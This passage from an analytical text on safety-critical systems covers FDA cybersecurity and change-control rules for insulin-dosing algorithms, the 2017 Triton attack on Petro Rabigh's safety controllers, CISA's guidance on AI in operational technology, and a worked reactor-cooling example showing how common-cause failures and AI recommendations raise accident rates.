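The FDA's guidance *Cybersecurity in Medical Devices*, issued in 2023 and since revised, explains what evidence manufacturers should submit. They should provide a threat model, which is an analysis of who might attack the system, how, and with what effect. They should assume that an attacker controls the network and can change, block or repeat messages. They should also test the system's security, including with attempted break-ins, and provide diagrams of how the parts connect and how updates reach them.

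Manufacturers should also judge a flaw by how easily someone could exploit it, because past incidents don't reliably predict future attacks. By that standard, the lack of known injuries from the MiniMed flaw was not a good reason to leave the pumps in use.

The guidance is not binding, although section 524B is. Manufacturers also produce most of the evidence themselves. At the *Hospital Diabetes Meeting 2020*, the physician David Klonoff pointed out that the FDA requires proof of good cybersecurity but does not test devices itself. Section 524B applies to new applications, so it does not force a company to update a pump it sold ten years ago.

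### Algorithms that change after approval

A manufacturer normally needs a new FDA review before it makes a change that could significantly affect a device's safety or effectiveness. A patch that only strengthens security usually doesn't need one, so this requirement should not delay urgent security fixes.

Because the Control-IQ controller is a separate device from the pump, Tandem could submit a new algorithm without having the FDA reconsider the pump's motor and tubing. The FDA first authorised Control-IQ for people aged 14 and over. In June 2020 it cleared a new application that extended use to children aged 6 to 13 and required Tandem to include them in the follow-up study, according to Innolitics. The FDA received the application for a later version, Control-IQ+, on 14 March 2025 and cleared it on 21 May.

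Ten weeks is manageable for an occasional new version but slow for a developer who wants to retrain an AI model every month. Congress therefore allowed predetermined change control plans in the same 2022 law that created section 524B. In such a plan, the manufacturer describes the changes it expects to make, the method and tests it will use for each, and the possible benefits and risks. If the FDA authorises the plan, the manufacturer can make those changes without another application. The FDA published final guidance on these plans for AI-enabled devices in December 2024.

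A plan for a dosing controller might let the company retrain the glucose prediction on data from new users, but release a new version only if it meets fixed accuracy targets on a separate set of patients and never recommends more insulin than a stated limit. The plan would not normally cover extending the controller to a new disease, because the device has to keep its intended use.

A plan checks changes to the algorithm, but its tests can miss harm, just as a check on doses can. If the test data include few young children, a new version could meet every target and still give them too much insulin. The manufacturer therefore also needs to monitor how each version performs in use and be able to return to the previous one.

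## Industrial plants: the Triton attack and official guidance on AI

A refinery or chemical plant usually has two computer systems connected to the same equipment. The process control system runs the plant by opening valves, setting pump speeds and holding temperatures steady. The safety instrumented system acts only when a measurement crosses a fixed limit, shutting down the dangerous part of the process. In 2017, attackers got into the safety system of a petrochemical plant in Saudi Arabia.

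A safety system measures the physical result, whereas the gates in earlier sections check commands. It closes the inlet valve if the pressure in a vessel gets too high, whether the cause was a bad command, a broken pump or a long series of small adjustments. A gate that checks each action separately can miss such a series, as it missed the ten payments of 499 dollars. But measuring the result protects only against hazards that someone has identified and that sensors can detect in time. It also requires a safe state to return to, which usually exists in a plant but not after an email has been sent.

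### Why the two systems are separate

The main reason for separation is that a fault in the control system can create the danger, so the same fault must not disable the protection. The 61508 Association's *Integrated and Separate* (2017), a guide from an industry group, adds practical reasons. Engineers change the control system far more often than the safety system, and separation keeps those changes from affecting safety. Separation also leaves less to analyse and test, as a small trusted computing base does.

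The international standard for these systems is IEC 61511. Its original text, IEC (2003), contains several requirements about independence:

- A control system that does not itself meet the standard must be separate enough that it can't compromise the safety system.
- The two systems may exchange data. They may share a device whose failure would both create a danger and weaken the protection, such as a sensor, only if an analysis shows that the overall risk is acceptable.
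- The company must assess whether a single cause could disable several layers of protection.
- Operators normally need a way to shut the plant down without the safety system's computer, such as an emergency stop button.
- An ordinary control system may count as a layer of protection, but the company must assume that it reduces the risk less than tenfold.

The current edition dates from 2016. It still has the tenfold ceiling and the assessment of shared causes, according to a podcast by the engineering consultancy Kenexis.

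The standard doesn't require the systems to be physically disconnected. The 61508 Association describes a range of designs, from two systems that share no components to a single controller that does both jobs. Some designs in between have separate controllers on a shared network, sometimes with one workstation for programming both. The association warns that the cybersecurity risk grows as the systems become more integrated.

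### How a shared cause undoes the protection

Suppose a fault raises the pressure in a vessel to a dangerous level once a year. The plant has two layers of protection, a safety system and a mechanical relief valve, and each fails one time in 100. If the failures are independent, the chance that both layers fail is

0.01 × 0.01 = 0.0001

and the plant can expect an accident once in 10,000 years.

Now suppose that a tenth of each layer's failures have a common cause. The standard suggests checking for one such cause, material that plugs both the relief valve and the safety system's sensors. The chance that both layers fail becomes

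0.1 × 0.01 + (0.9 × 0.01)² ≈ 0.0011

or about one accident in 925 years. The tenth is an assumption for illustration, but even this modest overlap makes accidents almost 11 times as frequent. Better equipment only partly compensates. If each layer failed one time in 1,000, independent layers would allow one accident in a million years. With the same share of common failures, the figure would be about one in 9,900.

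These formulas treat failures as chance events, so they don't apply to an attacker who controls both systems. Such an attacker can raise the pressure and disable the safety system at the same time. The mechanical relief valve may still work, because malware cannot reprogram it.

### The attack at Petro Rabigh

The attack went unnoticed at first. According to an article reposted by the mailing list InfoSec News, the safety system halted the plant in June 2017 and people blamed a mechanical fault. In August it halted the plant again. Sobczak (2019) reports in *The Inside Story Of The World's Most Dangerous Malware* that the control room engineers saw nothing unusual on their screens or on the plant floor.

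The plant's operator, Petro Rabigh, called in a team from the oil company Saudi Aramco, which owned 37.5% of it. According to E&E News, which published Sobczak's investigation, the team found the malware later named Triton, along with a lot of other malware of unknown origin.

Triton targeted an industrial plant's safety controllers. *Cyber Risk to Mission Case Study* (2022), published on a US defence website, explains that when Triton tried to reprogram the controllers, a check on their code failed and they shut the plant down safely. Dan Scali, who led the security company FireEye's investigation, thought the attackers may not have fully intended the shutdown, according to CSHub's *Incident Of The Week*. They seem to have been exploring the network. The controllers' fail-safe design worked, but the attackers' mistake triggered it. If they had disabled the protection without causing a shutdown,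 the plant could have kept running without anyone knowing that the safety system no longer worked.

The accounts identify four weaknesses that helped the attackers or delayed their discovery:

1. **The company's firewall.** A poor configuration gave them a foothold in the corporate computers, and from there they moved into the plant's networks.
2. **The safety network.** The safety system was connected to the plant's operations network, against recommended practice, according to findings by the security company Dragos in Automation World's *Cyber Attack Hits Safety System in Critical Infrastructure*.
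3. **The keys.** Each safety controller had a physical key switch, and staff had left the switches in the position that allows reprogramming.
4. **The June shutdown.** The mistaken diagnosis gave the attackers about two more months.

The key switch was a good safeguard because nobody can turn a key over a network, but it slowed legitimate work. The podcast Darknet Diaries describes a ten-minute walk from the control room to the controllers, and says that six controllers were in the programming position on the Friday evening of the attack. As with approval fatigue, people weakened a safeguard because it kept interrupting them. Schneider Electric, which made the controllers, told customers to remove the keys after use and to isolate the safety network from the rest of the plant.

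Petro Rabigh had separate safety controllers, but a chain of network connections linked them to the corporate computers. An audit that checked only whether the plant had two systems would have missed those connections.

### What the agencies advise about AI

CISA's *Principles for the Secure Integration of Artificial Intelligence in Operational Technology* aims to prevent AI from creating new connections of this kind. Operational technology means the computers that monitor and control physical equipment. CISA wrote the guidance with Australia's cyber agency and seven other agencies, and published it on 3 December 2025.

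The agencies advise that AI such as language models "almost certainly should not be used to make safety decisions" in these plants. They say AI may be too unreliable for critical decisions and can invent false information. They are less clear about smaller models. Their table of current and possible uses includes controllers that run small predictive models for tasks such as "maintaining a known safe state", which sounds much like a safety decision.

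The agencies prefer designs that send data out of the plant network to the AI without giving it a standing connection back in. Where data must reach the business network, they recommend one-way transfer. A company that followed this advice for its AI could still have a badly configured firewall elsewhere, like the one at Petro Rabigh. AI features built into equipment can also open a new route into the plant network, because some need an internet connection. The agencies suggest asking vendors whether such products can work without internet access, and letting the operator control when AI features are on.

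**Human responsibility.** The agencies write, "Ultimately, humans are responsible for functional safety." They advise against letting AI actively control equipment without a person involved, and warn that problems can escalate before operators notice them. People also need to be able to intervene, and the agencies recognise that staff who rely on AI may lose the skills to run the plant without it. They recommend training people to check the AI's output against other evidence, including separate sensors and their own senses.

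Any process that uses AI should be able to return to conventional automation or manual operation, and the owner should decide in advance how poor the AI's performance must be to trigger the switch. Conventional automation will often be more realistic than manual operation. The IT Nerd (2026), in an article on the security of industrial systems, cites a survey in which only 15% of respondents said their organisations could fully sustain manual operation for more than 48 hours.

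The advice is sensible, but it is voluntary and contains few numbers. It doesn't specify how reliable an AI system has to be, or how often a person may approve its recommendations before approval becomes a formality.

### Changes since December 2025

Most of the later work is also voluntary or unfinished. The guidance on AI agents from the Australian Signals Directorate and its partners, discussed earlier, tells organisations never to give agents broad or unrestricted access to critical systems. In April 2026, *Concept Note* (Sheh and Stanley, 2026) announced that NIST would write a profile on AI in critical infrastructure. The profile is to cover the need for predictable behaviour, gradual rather than sudden loss of function, and fail-safe operation. Safety systems already provide these, but a language model that can give different answers to the same question will have trouble behaving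 predictably.

NIST has also drafted a new version of its general guide to securing industrial systems. The September announcement, *Guide to Operational Technology (OT) Security* (2026), lists changes that include advice on network monitoring and zero trust, but none specific to AI. The comment period closed on 30 November.

Standards bodies have addressed the design of the safety system in more detail. ISO/IEC's *Artificial intelligence — Functional safety and AI systems* (2024), a technical report published before the agencies' guidance, covers the use of safety functions without AI to protect equipment that AI controls. A planned specification, described in DIN's *Artificial intelligence*, would turn this into requirements. A new edition of part of IEC 61508, the general standard on which IEC 61511 builds, would add requirements on common-cause failures, according to a listing of the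 IEC draft. IEC 61511 itself has not changed. The package that IEC (2026) published in February still contains the 2016 edition with a 2017 amendment.

Greig (2026), in *Cyber experts call on CISA to create mandatory federal OT rules*, reports that an industry coalition asked CISA in October to set binding minimum standards for equipment owned by US federal agencies. The coalition pointed to attacks on hundreds of water systems in at least 12 states. Many of the affected devices were needlessly connected to the internet, had default passwords or none, and shared a network with unrelated systems. These weaknesses don't involve AI, and fixing them would probably protect more plants than any rule about AI models.

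### Testing the advice on a pump

Suppose a chemical reactor gives off heat and a pump circulates cooling water around it. With the pump at 80% of full speed, the reactor stays at 150°C, and each percentage point drop in pump speed makes it 1°C hotter. An independent safety system shuts down the plant if the reactor reaches 180°C.

An AI system receives the plant's data over a one-way link and recommends pump speeds that save electricity. An operator reads each recommendation and enters it into the control system if it looks right. This arrangement follows the agencies' advice on safety decisions, data transfer and human involvement.

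| What goes wrong | What the operator does | What the safety system does |
|---|---|---|
| The AI recommends 8% instead of 80% | Very probably rejects it | Stops the plant if the operator approves it |
| The AI recommends 45%, which would lead to 185°C | May approve it | Stops the plant at 180°C |
| An intruder in the control system lowers the speed after approval | May not notice | Stops the plant |
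| The only temperature sensor, which everyone relies on, reads 40°C too low | Sees a normal temperature | Acts only when the reactor is really at 220°C |
| An intruder controls both systems | May see nothing unusual | Does nothing |
| The AI recommends 60%, which leads to 170°C and spoils the product | May approve it | Does nothing, because 170°C is within the limit |

The faulty sensor is a common-cause failure. It gives the AI, the operator and the safety system the same wrong reading, so having three layers doesn't help. A separate sensor for the safety system would fix this, and an operator who checked another thermometer might also catch the error. If an intruder controls both systems, the plant has only its mechanical protection and the emergency stop button. The button helps only if someone notices the danger in time to press it, and the engineers at Petro Rabigh noticed nothing.

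The operator is also less independent of the AI than the table suggests. If the AI explains that cooler weather makes 45% safe, the operator may have no other source for that claim. The one-way link keeps an attacker from using the AI as a network route into the plant, but the operator carries the AI's recommendations across by hand, so an attacker who can alter them can still influence the pump.

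The 60% setting causes permitted harm. The reactor is in no danger at 170°C, but the extra heat creates an impurity, and the company finds out when customers return the product. Lowering the safety limit to 165°C would prevent this but would also stop the plant whenever another product needed 170°C. A better solution is a separate quality limit for each product, which works only if someone already knows that the heat causes the impurity. The agencies also recommend monitoring for unusual AI output. That would probably flag a sudden drop from 80% to 60%, but it could miss a drop of one percentage point a week for 20 weeks.

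Adding the AI can make the plant more dangerous even if the safety system works as well as before. Suppose the safety system fails one time in 100 and, before the AI was added, the plant needed it once every ten years. One accident would then be expected every 1,000 years. If the operator now approves one dangerous recommendation a year, the plant needs the safety system about 11 times as often, and one accident is expected about every 90 years. IEC 61511 requires companies to state how often they expect to need each safety function and why. An owner who adds an AI system should therefore revise that estimate first, and may find that the plant needs a more reliable safety system or another layer of protection.
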